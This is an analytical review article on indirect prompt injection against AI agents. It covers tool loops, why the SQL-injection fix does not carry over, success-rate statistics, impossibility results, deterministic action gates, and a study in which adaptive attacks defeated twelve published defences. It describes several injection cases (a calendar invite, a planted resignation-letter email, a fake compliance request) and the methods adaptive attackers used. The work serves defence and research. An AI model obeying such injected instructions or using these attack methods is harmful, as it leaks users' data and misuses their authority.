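# Can general-purpose AI agents be secured against injected instructions, and what does a gate on their actions settle?

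## Agents, injected instructions and what counts as a guarantee

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, such as an email account, a file system or a web browser, that chooses actions to carry out a user's request. Much of what an agent reads, such as incoming mail, web pages, shared documents and calendar invitations, comes from strangers. In a prompt injection attack, someone hides instructions in that material and the model acts on them against the user's intent. The agent might use the user's permissions to forward private mail, run a program or send phishing links to the user's colleagues. Some authors call this indirect prompt injection or agent hijacking, to distinguish it from attacks by the user.

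An attacker only needs a way to put text where the model will read it, not access to the model itself or to the user's computer. Microsoft (2025) points out that a plain text file is enough, and that images, audio and video carry the same risk if the model accepts them. "Untrusted content" means any text, image, audio or video that an attacker could have created or altered.

### One agent loop

Suppose a user asks an assistant with access to a calendar and a mailbox to send today's schedule to a boss, John Doe. The example comes from Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*. A language model cannot open a calendar. It can only produce text, and, as Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains for the company's Claude models, some of that text takes the form of a structured request that ordinary program code then carries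 out. The exchange runs like this:

1. The program sends the model the user's request, along with a list of the available tools and the arguments each one takes.
2. The model replies with a tool call: read the calendar for today.
3. The program runs the call and gets the day's entries back as text.
4. The program sends the model the whole conversation again, now with the calendar text added.
5. The model replies with another tool call: send an email to John Doe's address, with a given body. The program sends it and reports back, and the loop continues until the model stops asking for tools.

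The injection enters at step 4. For example, one entry might be an invitation from an outsider, with a description field that contains an instruction to also send the user's recent mail to a second address. The calendar tool has worked correctly by returning what was in the calendar, but the model now chooses its next call from a text that contains both the user's sentence and the outsider's.

That text contains labels. According to *Handle tool calls*, Anthropic's interface takes a tool's output in a message with the role "user", inside a block marked as a tool result. OpenAI publishes a library that turns a conversation, including tool output, into a single sequence of tokens (the word fragments that a model processes), with special markers showing where each speaker starts. These markers are also tokens. Training teaches the model to give them weight, but no mechanism outside the model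 makes it do so.

In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) measured how much role markers affect which speaker a model takes a passage to come from. They trained small classifiers to detect the perceived speaker from the model's internal activations, using identical text wrapped in different markers so that the classifiers could learn only the markers' effect. They then marked an entire conversation about gardening as user text. The classifiers still gave passages in the style of the model's own reasoning an 85% probability of being reasoning and a 2% probability of being user text. Across 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where confusion about the speaker was lowest to 70% where it was highest. So the models' internal representation of who is speaking depends largely on style, which the attacker controls.

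Researchers have also tried to build a firmer separation between instructions and data into the model itself. *ASIDE* (2025), one such attempt, measures this separation on 9,160 pairs of instructions and inputs. The test places an unrelated instruction in either the instruction part or the data part, and a model scores well if it follows the instruction in the first and ignores it in the second. A better score is useful, but it is an average over test cases, and an attacker can look for cases where the separation fails.

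### The confused deputy, and why the SQL remedy does not carry over

Computer security has long used the term "confused deputy" for a program that someone tricks into using its authority on their behalf. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* tells a "nearly true" story about a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler had permission to write in its home directory because it kept usage statistics there. It also let users name a file to receive debugging output. One user named the billing file, which was in the same directory. The user had no right to overwrite that file, but the compiler did, and the billing records were lost.

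Hardy concluded that the compiler held authority from two parties and had no way to keep the two apart. The remedy was the capability, a reference that both identifies a file and carries permission to write to it. If the compiler writes debugging output only through a capability supplied by the user, it can send that output only to a file the user could write to.

An agent that follows instructions in a calendar entry is also a confused deputy, because it holds the user's authority over the mailbox while an outsider steers it. Hardy's compiler had separate pieces of code for statistics and debugging output, so a programmer could attach the right authority to each, but a language model has no separate code for handling the user's instructions and the text of a calendar entry. That is roughly why David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, calls the model an "inherently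 confusable deputy" in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. The title refers to a comparison that many security professionals make first.

Programs query databases in a language called SQL. A careless program builds a query by pasting a visitor's text into a string of SQL, so a visitor who types SQL can change what the query does. Programmers first tried to strip out dangerous input, an approach that CISA and the FBI's *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024) describes as brittle and often possible to bypass. Parameterised queries work better. The program gives the database a query containing a placeholder and supplies the visitor's text separately as the value. The query's structure is already fixed by then, so the database treats the text as data whatever it contains. MySQL, a widely used database system, has supported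 parameterised queries since 2004. They eliminate this whole class of attack where programmers use them consistently.

The remedy for SQL injection depends on the database having a grammar that separates commands from values. A language model has no such grammar. As David C puts it, there is only ever a "next token". Strict separation would also be undesirable, because a user who tells an agent to "deal with the invitations in my inbox" wants the invitations to affect what it does. David C concludes that prompt injection may never be fixed as completely as SQL injection was, and advises designers to focus on safeguards outside the model that constrain what the system can do.

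### A low rate, a guarantee and a correct result

People who call an agent "secure against prompt injection" may mean any of three things, and evidence for one is often weak evidence for another.

They may mean that attacks rarely work. The usual measure is the attack success rate, the share of attempts or of test scenarios in which the attacker gets the intended effect. *AgentDojo* (2024), a test suite that many researchers use, has 97 agent tasks and 629 injection tests. A defence that lowers the rate without ruling attacks out is a heuristic defence, and the best current models with such defences post very low rates. But a rate describes the attacks that somebody tried. Even zero successes in 629 tests would be compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true rate of just under 0.5%, and that calculation already supposes that real attackers draw their attacks at random from the same pool. They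 don't. An adaptive attacker knows the defence and keeps revising the attack against it. In a public contest covered in CAISI's *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition*, more than 400 participants made over 250,000 attempts against 13 leading models, and every model fell at least once. (CAISI is the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation.)

A small rate per attempt also grows with repetition. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is

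1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*

With *p* = 1%, the chance that at least one attempt succeeds is 1% for one attempt, 9.6% for ten and 63.4% for a hundred, and an attacker can send a hundred emails for almost nothing.

However, independence is a strong assumption, and relying on it can make the estimated risk too high or too low. Some targets are often much easier to attack than others, so an average success rate of 1% can combine very different rates. *Statistical Estimation of Adversarial Risk in Large Language Models under Best-of-N Sampling* (Feng, Liu and colleagues, 2026) models this by letting *p* vary across targets according to a beta distribution, a flexible family of curves between 0 and 1. The figures below all assume an average success rate of 1% per attempt. The middle row applies the paper's formula with illustrative parameters (α = 0.1, β = 9.9).

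| How the 1% is spread over targets | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Every target has *p* = 1% | 1% | 9.6% | 63.4% |
| *p* varies widely between targets | 1% | 7.0% | 21.7% |
| One target in 100 always falls, the rest never | 1% | 1% | 1% |

Feng and colleagues tested their model on jailbreaks, which are attempts to make an AI produce forbidden content, not on injections. They found that one attack method could do worse than another on a single try but overtake it by the fifteenth, so a ranking of defences based on single attempts may not hold when attacks are repeated.

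Repeated attempts also raise an attack's chance of success against agents. In CAISI's *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, testers repeated five injection tasks 25 times each against an agent running a Claude model from October 2024. The average success rate across the tasks rose from 57% after one attempt to 80% after 25. If every attempt at every task had an independent 57% chance of success, 25 attempts would almost certainly have produced at least one success on each task. Sending the same text again also helps less than sending new text, because a model that ignored it once is somewhat more likely to ignore it again. In *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component*, Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar (2026) estimated this effect for one small model that obeyed the best attack wording about half the time. The chance of at least one success in ten attempts was 99.6%, but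 fell to 93.6% when the attacker sent the same prompt every time.

An attacker who learns between attempts has the opposite effect, because *p* rises. Red-teamers working with CAISI developed new attacks against that same Claude model. The strongest succeeded 81% of the time on tasks held back from development, compared with 11% for the strongest existing attack. The formula is best read as a warning about small values of *p*, and it gives neither an upper nor a lower bound on a real attacker's success rate.

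A guarantee is a claim that a defined class of harmful outcomes cannot occur under stated assumptions, whatever the attacker writes. For example, "This agent sends no email to anyone except John Doe" could be a guarantee, and repeated attempts would not weaken it while the assumptions hold. One way to make "whatever the attacker writes" precise is to assume that the attacker controls the model, instead of modelling how injected text influences it. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) uses a version of this assumption in which the attacker chooses how the model follows instructions.

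Choosing the class of outcomes is hard. The classical condition, noninterference, requires that untrusted content have no effect on what protected parts of the system do. Dongol rejects it as too strong because a useful agent lets such content influence its actions and sometimes discloses the user's data by design. Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same checks, but with a model that never follows instructions in untrusted content. The real agent passes if it has no leak that the reference agent lacks. This guarantee is weaker than it may sound because it allows leaks built into the plan, which both agents share.

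Third, people may mean that the user's task comes out right. In the schedule example, suppose the agent's actions are fixed in advance, so that it reads today's calendar and then sends one email to John Doe. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that an injection in the calendar can still control the whole body of that email. It can move a meeting to the wrong hour or invent one. The boss then receives a false schedule even though every action was permitted and the guarantee held. This is harm through permitted actions. A guarantee about actions also doesn't ensure that the task gets done, since an attacker may only want the agent to try something forbidden and get stuck.

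### The gate

A gate checks each tool call in the loop before the program runs it, and either allows or blocks it. Papers also call it a reference monitor or runtime monitor. Its policy is the set of rules for which actions are allowed, with which arguments and data. For the schedule task, a policy might allow one reading of today's calendar and one email, to John Doe's address only. If the outsider's invitation causes the model to try to send mail somewhere else, the gate compares the recipient with the policy and blocks the call, however persuasive the invitation was.

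That holds for a deterministic gate, which is made of ordinary code and fixed rules, so its decision on a given action and recorded state does not depend on a model's judgment. In a model-based gate, a language model or trained classifier decides, perhaps by assessing whether an action fits the user's request. It can handle situations that nobody wrote a rule for, but an attacker can fool it. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues observe that an attacker facing such a detector must deceive two systems instead of one, which makes an attack harder but does not guarantee that it will fail. Microsoft makes the same distinction between probabilistic and deterministic defences, and uses both.

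A deterministic gate can still be wrong, because if its rule is bad, it enforces that bad rule every time. The guarantee depends on the trusted base, the components that must all work correctly for it to hold. Aljumaily and colleagues include the gate, the policy, the code of the tools, the component that tracks untrusted data and the channel through which a human approves actions. The approach is attractive because the trusted base does not include the model. Their analysis excludes attacks on the trusted components, denial of service and covert channels (ways of signalling information through side effects).

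A gate also has to cover every action. If a policy restricts who the email tool can send to, but the agent can write and run a script that sends mail by another route, the agent can bypass the restriction. *Kairos* (2026) places the gate at the boundary of the isolated environment in which the agent runs, so that the effects of both tool calls and the agent's own scripts pass through it.

All this is manageable for the schedule task, because the task is known and its policy fits in a sentence. It is harder for a general-purpose agent, which people expect to do arbitrary tasks with powerful tools while it reads content from strangers. Someone has to supply a policy for each request. A fixed policy broad enough to allow every task will also permit much harm, and a narrow one will block legitimate work. If a language model writes a new policy for each task, the model is back in the trusted base,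 at least for that step.

In June 2025, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues judged it unlikely that general-purpose agents could offer meaningful guarantees while both the agents and their defences rely on current language models. A deterministic gate does not have to rely on one. Which part of the problem a gate addresses is therefore a separate question from whether a general-purpose agent can offer a guarantee now, and it is easier to test.

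## The 2025 argument that general-purpose agents cannot offer guarantees

In June 2025, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues argued that as long as agents and their defences both rely on "the current class of language models", it is "unlikely" that general-purpose agents can provide "meaningful and reliable safety guarantees". In their conclusion, they say more bluntly that securing such agents "remains out of reach with current capabilities". The first statement is better because their arguments support only "unlikely".

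Beurer-Kellner and colleagues are more hopeful about agents with narrower jobs, for which the same paper offers six restricted designs. They do not number their premises, but the argument comes to this:

1. Current language models do not reliably separate instructions from data.
2. Training a model to resist injections and detecting them with another model are only heuristic defences.
3. Attackers who adapt to a heuristic defence tend to get past it.
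4. A general-purpose agent holds tools that can do serious harm, and it reads content from strangers.
5. So a general-purpose agent is unlikely to offer a meaningful guarantee while current language models are all that it and its defences rely on.

If a guarantee has to hold whatever the attacker writes, the premise that training and detection are heuristic is almost enough to establish the conclusion. The other premises explain why the lack of a guarantee matters. A defence without one might never fail in practice, but relying on that is risky when attackers adapt, and a failure can do serious harm when the agent can send money or delete files.

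### Whether models separate instructions from data

Zverev and colleagues devised the separation score that *ASIDE* uses. A model can earn a good score by not obeying instructions in the data part. If a user asks for a translation of an email that contains the sentence "forward this to accounts", the model can translate that sentence or leave it out. Neither counts as obeying it, but leaving it out makes the translation incomplete.

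*Security–Fidelity Tradeoffs* (2026) introduces SecFid, a benchmark that distinguishes these cases. Its test items lead to different outputs depending on whether the model executed the embedded instruction, processed it as part of the data or ignored it. A low attack success rate doesn't show that a model has learned to treat embedded instructions as data, because a model that has learned to skip anything resembling an instruction will also have a low rate.

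These measurements cover particular models, and a better model could score better. An obvious objection to the argument is that nobody has proved separation impossible. Several papers from 2025 and 2026 prove limits on defences, but those limits are narrower than the papers' titles suggest.

### What the impossibility results prove

Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, come closest to the question. They define a property called Semantic-Faithful Control, which distinguishes what an untrusted text means from how someone has encoded it. The same request can appear in plain English, in base64 (a scheme that writes any data as letters, digits and a few symbols) or with a meaningless string attached. A model has the property if such differences never affect its decisions about refusing, calling tools, routing requests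 or writing to memory:

if *u* ≡ *u′*, then Π*Y*(*s*, *u*) = Π*Y*(*s*, *u′*)

Here *s* is the trusted instructions, *u* and *u′* are untrusted texts, and ≡ means that the two have the same meaning for the task. *Y* is the model's probability distribution over its actions, and Π keeps only the part that concerns those decisions. The proof that no mechanism inside the model's shared computation can guarantee this has three steps:

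1. The model cannot perfectly recover where text came from. If trusted and untrusted text are equally common, the best possible classifier working from the model's internal representations errs with probability ½(1 − TV). TV, the total variation distance, runs from 0 for identical distributions to 1 for distributions that never overlap. At TV = 0.9, the best classifier still errs 5% of the time.
2. Untrusted text reaches the decision. Attention, the operation by which these models combine information from different positions in a text, feeds it into the same computation that produces the tool call.
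3. Training covers a finite number of encodings, while a single meaning can have endlessly many. Correct behaviour on the encodings in the training set does not entail correct behaviour on the rest.

The argument depends mostly on its last step, which is a limit on evidence. Correct behaviour on a finite sample proves nothing about the remaining cases, as with any program that people check only by example. This does not mean that every trained model misbehaves somewhere, since a model that refused every request would have the property exactly, though it would be useless. The proof also does not consider verifying a finished model from its weights instead of from examples.

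The first step also has a gap. The overlap is trivial for single words, because "the" enters the model in the same form whoever wrote it. Pant and colleagues assume that representations also overlap in the later layers, where decisions form. They support this with measurements on a small model, Llama 3.1 8B. The distance between its internal states for system prompts and for user messages, measured as maximum mean discrepancy, was 0.61 at the input, 0.91 at layer 8 and 0.76 at layer 31. But this measure can take moderate values even when a classifier could separate the two groups without error, so the figures do not establish an overlap.

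The property also differs from security against injection. An agent that obeyed every order in every email, however it was encoded, would satisfy the definition, because the definition lets decisions depend on meaning. A model can also violate the definition harmlessly, because the equation requires the probabilities to match exactly. When Pant and colleagues gave two small models the rules of a financial service and tried five known injection techniques, both models refused all five. The injected text changed the length and wording of the replies but not the decision.

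Bhatt, Munshi and colleagues (2026), in *The Defense Trilemma*, prove a limit on a different kind of defence, a wrapper that rewrites each prompt before the model sees it. They show that such a wrapper cannot have all three of these properties:

- It is continuous, meaning that similar prompts get similar rewrites.
- It leaves safe prompts unchanged.
- It makes every output safe.

A simplified example shows why. Let prompts be the numbers from 0 to 1, let each number be its own danger score, and call a prompt safe if it scores below 0.5. The wrapper leaves safe prompts such as 0.49, 0.499 and 0.4999 unchanged. If it is continuous, it must also leave 0.5 unchanged, even though 0.5 is not safe. Bhatt and colleagues proved the general case and checked the whole theory with Lean, a program that verifies proofs.

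The basic theorem shows only that some prompts exactly on the threshold get through. To show that clearly dangerous prompts also get through, Bhatt and colleagues need a further condition, that danger rises faster near the threshold than the wrapper can reduce it. Real prompts are strings of separate symbols, with no continuous path from one to the next. In the version for finite sets, a wrapper that makes every prompt safe must map some different prompts to the same rewrite. A filter that replaces every attack with a blank message does this, and few users would object. Bhatt and colleagues exclude training, changes to the model's architecture, hard blocklists, checks on outputs and systems that may reject a prompt.

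*On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (2025) shows that, under certain cryptographic assumptions, filtering prompts or responses for harmful content can be computationally infeasible without access to the model's internals. This weakens the case for relying on a separate filter to catch all harmful text. It is less relevant to a check that compares an email's recipient with a list, because that check does not have to judge whether the content is harmful.

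So the theorems give good reasons to distrust a guarantee based only on training examples or input filters. But none of them shows that every language model must confuse instructions with data, so it is still right to say only that general-purpose agents are "unlikely" to offer guarantees.

### Training, detection and attackers who adapt

Detectors are heuristic defences that can look sound but miss the attack that matters. *Confidently Wrong* (2026) tested three of them on a harmlessly worded instruction placed inside an ordinary document. They scored it 0.070, 0.005 and 0.003, all close to "no injection". ProtectAI-v2, which gave the 0.070, had scored such instructions at 0.523 when they stood alone. Meaningless padding of the same length raised its score, so the coherent text, rather than the added length, hid the attack. The other two detectors, both sizes of Prompt-Guard-2, responded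 mainly to how harmful a request sounded, and an instruction to forward a report sounds harmless.

*PIShield* (2025) offers evidence on the other side. It describes a detector that reads a language model's internal representations, and it reports that the detector works even against strong adaptive attacks. But it concedes that the detector may flag harmless instructions that belong in the data, and that the line between harmless and malicious instructions is often ambiguous. More training data would not remove that ambiguity. Whether "please send the signed form to Anna" is an injection depends on what the user asked the agent to do, which a detector cannot determine by looking for instruction-like text.

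An attacker who adapts to a detector can defeat it completely. One of the detectors in *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) uses a table of synonyms to score how closely a text matches known attack phrases. It caught 19 of 20 attacks, but none of the 20 when the attacker knew the table. This was a small test of a simple detector. The next section covers much broader evidence, from attacks on twelve published defences.

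Training shows the same pattern, with a better outcome for the defender. By July 2026, OpenAI's latest models had saturated the common robustness tests, which could no longer be used to distinguish good models from better ones. OpenAI then trained an automated attacker, GPT-Red, and found its previous models "highly vulnerable" to it. It used the attacker to train GPT-5.6, and The Hacker News (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 Sol had six times fewer failures than GPT-5.5 on a benchmark of direct injections. Attacks are succeeding less often. But the older models' good test results were little help in predicting how they would perform against an attacker that did not yet exist, and the newer model's results have the same limitation.

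### The precedent from computer vision

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues support their pessimism about training with the precedent of adversarial examples. These are inputs, typically images with changes too small for a person to notice, that cause a classifier to give a wrong answer. The researchers cite work from 2014 and point out that the problem was still open after more than a decade of research. OpenAI draws the same connection in an explainer on prompt injection and calls robustness "a hard, open problem".

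One precedent is weak support for a generalisation, so the argument's strength depends on how similar the two problems are. Both involve neural networks that learn from examples and attackers who search for inputs the examples missed. Injection looks harder in two respects. First, vision researchers have certified defences, which Bhatt and colleagues mention as guarantees for fixed models, but these typically guarantee that no change below a certain size will alter the answer for a given image. An attacker who writes an entire email faces no such size limit, so this success does not carry over easily. Second, the correct response to a sentence changes with the user's request, while the correct label for a picture of a panda stays the same when the picture is slightly altered.

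In another respect, an agent's designer is better off than an image classifier's. The classifier has failed once it produces a wrong label, but a wrong tool call does nothing until ordinary code runs it, so the designer can add a check before that happens. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues draw the same lesson, citing computer vision when they argue that careful system design may keep an agent secure even if its model remains vulnerable. The computer vision precedent therefore lowers expectations for a guarantee that comes from training, but does not change the prospects of a gate.

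### What the condition leaves out

The claim covers only cases in which the agent and its defences both rely on a language model. A deterministic gate does not rely on one, so the claim does not apply to an agent behind such a gate. Pant and colleagues likewise exempt external policy engines from their theorem, because a component outside the model decides which tool calls go ahead. None of these arguments counts against a gate that blocks all email to unlisted addresses.

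The next dispute is whether an agent behind such a gate is still general-purpose. Passages in Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' paper support both answers. The introduction lists several isolation systems, including Debenedetti and colleagues' CaMeL architecture, and describes such proposals as mostly generic attempts at safe general-purpose agents. Later, the paper uses CaMeL as an example of one of its six designs, all of which are meant to stop agents from solving arbitrary tasks.

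Both descriptions can be fair, because an agent can be general in what users may ask of it or in how freely it may change course after reading something. A gate with a new policy for each request can allow a wide range of requests while restricting changes of course. This restriction causes problems when a stranger's text has to determine the next step, as when a user tells an agent to install a program by following the instructions on its website. A rule that untrusted text may never determine an action blocks the task. A rule that allows whatever commands the website lists gives no protection if an attacker has edited the page. The gate could require the user's approval, but Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that tired or overloaded people approve unsafe actions.

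A list of approved commands can even help the attacker. Poireault (2026), in *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*, reports a talk by Ariel Fogel, a security researcher who contributes to OWASP, a non-profit that publishes widely used lists of software risks. Fogel described attacks in which approved-command lists made exploitation easier because they already included the commands the hijacked agent needed.

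OpenAI made the tradeoff between generality and security explicit in February 2026 with Lockdown Mode, a ChatGPT setting that makes the assistant less capable but better protected against data leaks. The setting turns off certain tools by fixed rule, regardless of what the model decides. OpenAI disables a feature when it cannot give a strong deterministic guarantee of data safety. Browsing works only on cached pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network carrying a user's data. OpenAI considers the setting unnecessary for most users.

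### How far the NCSC and OpenAI agree

David C, writing for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) in December 2025, recommends the paper by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues but doubts that prompt injection will be fully fixed even in the future, whereas their claim covers only current models. David C offers designers a test rather than a general claim about which agents can offer guarantees. The test is to assume that an injection succeeds and ask what an attacker could do with direct access to the agent's tools. If the system cannot tolerate the remaining risk, "it may not be a good use case for ...".

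The same post repeats a rule from an exchange between the developers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from a party, its privileges should drop to that party's level. Applied strictly, this rules out general-purpose agents. An agent that had read a stranger's email could then do only what the stranger could do, which does not include sending mail from the user's account.

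Later official advice is stricter about uses. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), which the Australian Signals Directorate wrote with the NCSC and agencies from the United States, Canada and New Zealand, tells organisations to use agents only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks and never to grant them broad or unrestricted access, especially to sensitive data or critical systems. These limits exclude most of what people want a general-purpose agent for. However, the agencies worry not only about injection but also about excessive permissions, poor configuration and agents that pursue a goal in ways nobody intended, so the guidance is not a judgement on this argument alone.

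In August 2026 the NCSC added interim advice after several incidents in which AI models took unsanctioned actions. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*, it told organisations not to rely solely on safeguards built into a model or agent framework. For riskier deployments, it recommended isolated environments that refuse network connections by default where possible. This is close to Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' position, but the NCSC emphasises containing an agent that has already gone wrong.

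OpenAI agrees about the problem but draws a different conclusion. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) concerns the agent in OpenAI's Atlas browser, which the company calls one of its most general-purpose agentic features. The agent sees web pages and can click and type as the user would. OpenAI's automated attacker planted an email in a test inbox, containing instructions to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent found the email and sent the resignation letter.

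OpenAI concludes that prompt injection, like scams on the web, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", and that its nature makes deterministic guarantees "challenging". This admission carries some weight because a company that sells such an agent has little reason to exaggerate the problem. OpenAI still keeps the agent general-purpose, and aims to find attacks before outsiders do, train against them and make exploitation harder. It advises users to stay logged out of websites where the task allows it and to avoid requests such as "review my emails and take whatever action is needed", which means giving up some of the agent's generality.

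By March 2026, OpenAI was putting more emphasis on limiting damage. *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) argues that effective attacks increasingly resemble social engineering, the manipulation of people into giving away access or information. In one example, an email about a company restructuring included instructions for the assistant to look up an employee's details and submit them to a "compliance validation system". The attack worked in 50% of tests with one particular user request. In OpenAI's experience, filters that classify incoming text do not usually catch such attacks, because detecting them is as hard as detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. So ChatGPT also has a mechanism to detect when information from the conversation would be sent to a third party. It either blocks the transfer or shows the user what would be sent and asks for confirmation.

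OpenAI still expects the models themselves to improve, and thinks a maximally intelligent model would resist social engineering better than a person does. That may be right, but doing better than a person would not guarantee resistance, since people can be fooled too.

### The comparison with people who fall for fraud

It may seem unreasonable to demand a guarantee that an agent cannot be deceived, since nobody demands one for employees. Employees fall for fraudulent emails, and organisations give them access to money and records anyway.

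One reply is that deception scales differently with agents than with people. A story that fools one clerk may fail with the next, who has other habits and might phone a colleague. Copies of a model share the same weights, so a payload that works on one can work on many others in a similar setting, and an attacker can rehearse before sending it. Some payloads also work across different models. Pant and colleagues cite 2023 work by Zou and colleagues, in which appending meaningless strings to harmful requests caused several models to comply. Those strings were jailbreaks, not injections, and the restructuring email shows that an injection can fail half the time even against a single product, so a payload that works once will not necessarily work on every copy.

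Uniformity also helps the defender. OpenAI's automated attacker found new injections, and the company then trained the Atlas agent against them and gave every user the updated model. No employer can retrain an entire staff that way. Whether attackers or defenders gain more depends largely on who finds the attack first and how quickly the defender releases a fix.

The comparison also leaves out how organisations limit what their clerks can do. OpenAI describes a customer-service worker who can issue refunds. The employer expects some customers to mislead the worker, so software limits how much the worker can refund. That limit is a deterministic gate around a fallible person, and OpenAI recommends asking what controls would apply to a human in the agent's position.

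Controls designed for people may need changes before they suit agents. In Poireault's report, Fogel warns that isolation, lists of approved commands and manual review can all fail when the actor is an agent. In some cases the agent's own output redefined the boundaries of the environment that was supposed to contain it. A simple limit can also fail at scale. A cap of $50 per conversation keeps the loss from one deceived clerk small, but if the same message works in 10,000 conversations with an agent, the cap allows a loss of $500,000. The gate would also need a limit on the total, so it would have to keep a record across conversations.

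## The attacks that broke twelve published defences

Heuristic defences against injection usually come with good test results. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve recent defences with attacks adapted to each, and reached success rates above 90% against most of them. The developers of most of these defences had originally reported rates near zero. The paper's fourteen authors include several from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, and USENIX Security, a major security conference, accepted it for 2026.

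### Twelve defences in four families

Three of the defences change the prompt. Spotlighting marks untrusted text so that the model can distinguish it from instructions. Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, and RPO adds optimised wording meant to prevent jailbreaks.

Another three defences train the model itself. StruQ and MetaSecAlign train it to ignore instructions in the data part of its input, and Circuit Breakers trains it not to produce harmful content.

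Four are filters: Protect AI, PromptGuard, PIGuard and Google's Model Armor. Each uses a separate detector to block text that looks like an attack.

The last two defences depend on something the attacker supposedly doesn't know. Data Sentinel gives a model the untrusted text and tells it to ignore the text and repeat a secret key. If the model fails to repeat the key, it has presumably followed instructions in the text instead. MELON runs the agent twice, the second time replacing the user's request with a harmless request to summarise what the tools returned. A tool call that appears in both runs probably came from the untrusted text, so MELON flags it.

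Only eight of the twelve defences were tested against attacks on an agent with tools, in scenarios from AgentDojo. Of the other four, RPO and Circuit Breakers are defences against jailbreaks. An attack on StruQ only had to make the model print a specified phrase, and an attack on Data Sentinel had to make the model do one text-classification task in place of another.

### Propose, score, revise

All the attacks follow the same loop:

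1. Propose one or more candidate texts.
2. Give them to the defended system and score what happens.
3. Keep the most promising candidates.
4. Use them to produce the next batch, and repeat.

Scoring attempts is the hard part of a search attack. If the attacker learns only whether an attempt succeeded, it can't tell which early failures came closest, and the search is close to guessing. Nasr and colleagues' search attack therefore also used the defended model's replies, and a second language model rated each attempt from 1 to 10. Against filters, the attacker also saw the detector's confidence score, so it could tell which failed attempts had come close.

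The attackers differ mainly in how they propose candidates:

- The gradient attacker uses the model's internals to calculate which changes of wording would bring the desired output closer. Nasr and colleagues used it only against RPO.
- The reinforcement learning attacker is a language model that improves with practice. It had 32 sessions of five rounds for each test item, and training made the kinds of text that scored well more likely.
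- The search attacker needs no training. Gemini 2.5 Pro rewrote earlier candidates, with up to 800 queries per scenario, though progress usually levelled off after 100 to 200.
- The human attackers were some 500 people in an online contest with $20,000 in prizes. They could watch the agent's reasoning and tool calls as it ran.

Adapting to MELON raised the search attacker's success rate from 76% to 95% of scenarios when the agent's model was Llama 3.3 70B. Before the attacker knew that MELON was there, it succeeded because some injections happened to work only in the first run. Once it had a description of MELON, it began to write injections that behaved differently when the task was to summarise.

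### What the attacks achieved

Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, gives the values from the paper's main chart. The adaptive figures here are for the automated attacks.

| Family | Defence | What the attacker wanted | Fixed or weak attack | Adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompting | Spotlighting | A harmful tool call | 28% | 99% |
| Prompting | Prompt sandwiching | A harmful tool call | 21% | 95% |
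| Prompting | RPO | Forbidden content | 0% | 99% |
| Training | Circuit Breakers | Forbidden content | 8% | 100% |
| Training | StruQ | A set phrase | 62% | 100% |
| Training | MetaSecAlign | A harmful tool call | 5% | 96% |
| Filtering | Protect AI | A harmful tool call | 15% | 90% |
| Filtering | PromptGuard | A harmful tool call | 26% | 94% |
| Filtering | PIGuard | A harmful tool call | 0% | 71% |
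| Filtering | Model Armor | A harmful tool call | 0% | 90% |
| Secret knowledge | Data Sentinel | A different text task | 0% | 80% |
| Secret knowledge | MELON | A harmful tool call | 0% | 89% |

The figures in the column for fixed or weak attacks can differ from those the developers reported. For example, MetaSecAlign's developers reported 2% on AgentDojo, while this column gives 5%. The 0% for Model Armor is doubtful, because the paper's detailed results give 28% for the same filter with Gemini 2.5 Pro.

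For the search attack, the success rate is the share of scenarios in which at least one of up to 800 queries succeeded. Over that many tries, even a low chance per query can produce a high rate. But most of these defences failed long before the 800th query. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, the median number of queries before the first success was 13 with no defence and 14 with Spotlighting. If every query had the same independent chance, a median of 14 would mean about 5% per query. PIGuard did better, with a median of 46 in the scenarios where the attack succeeded, but it also cut the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 74% to 39%.

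The human contestants did better than the search. At least one person succeeded on each of the 29 scenarios that both attempted, while the search succeeded on 69% of them. That comparison favours the humans, since many people worked on each scenario and the search had a single run. Among the people who tried all 29 scenarios, the best broke 75% of them.

Some defences did make individual attempts harder. In the contest's one MELON scenario, 11.1% of submissions succeeded against an undefended Gemini 2.5 Pro with reasoning switched on, but only 0.4% succeeded with MELON in place. The base model also mattered. With GPT-5 Mini, the search attack succeeded in 75% of scenarios without a defence and 47% with Spotlighting, which is hard to reconcile with the paper's summary that prompting defences give no improvement over an undefended model. Making an attacker work harder has some value, but less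 than "near zero" suggested.

### Why a fixed test set misleads

AgentDojo's standard fixed attack never succeeded against GPT-5 Mini in these tests, even with no defence, so a defence that did nothing would have scored a 0% attack success rate. The search attack broke the same undefended model in three-quarters of scenarios.

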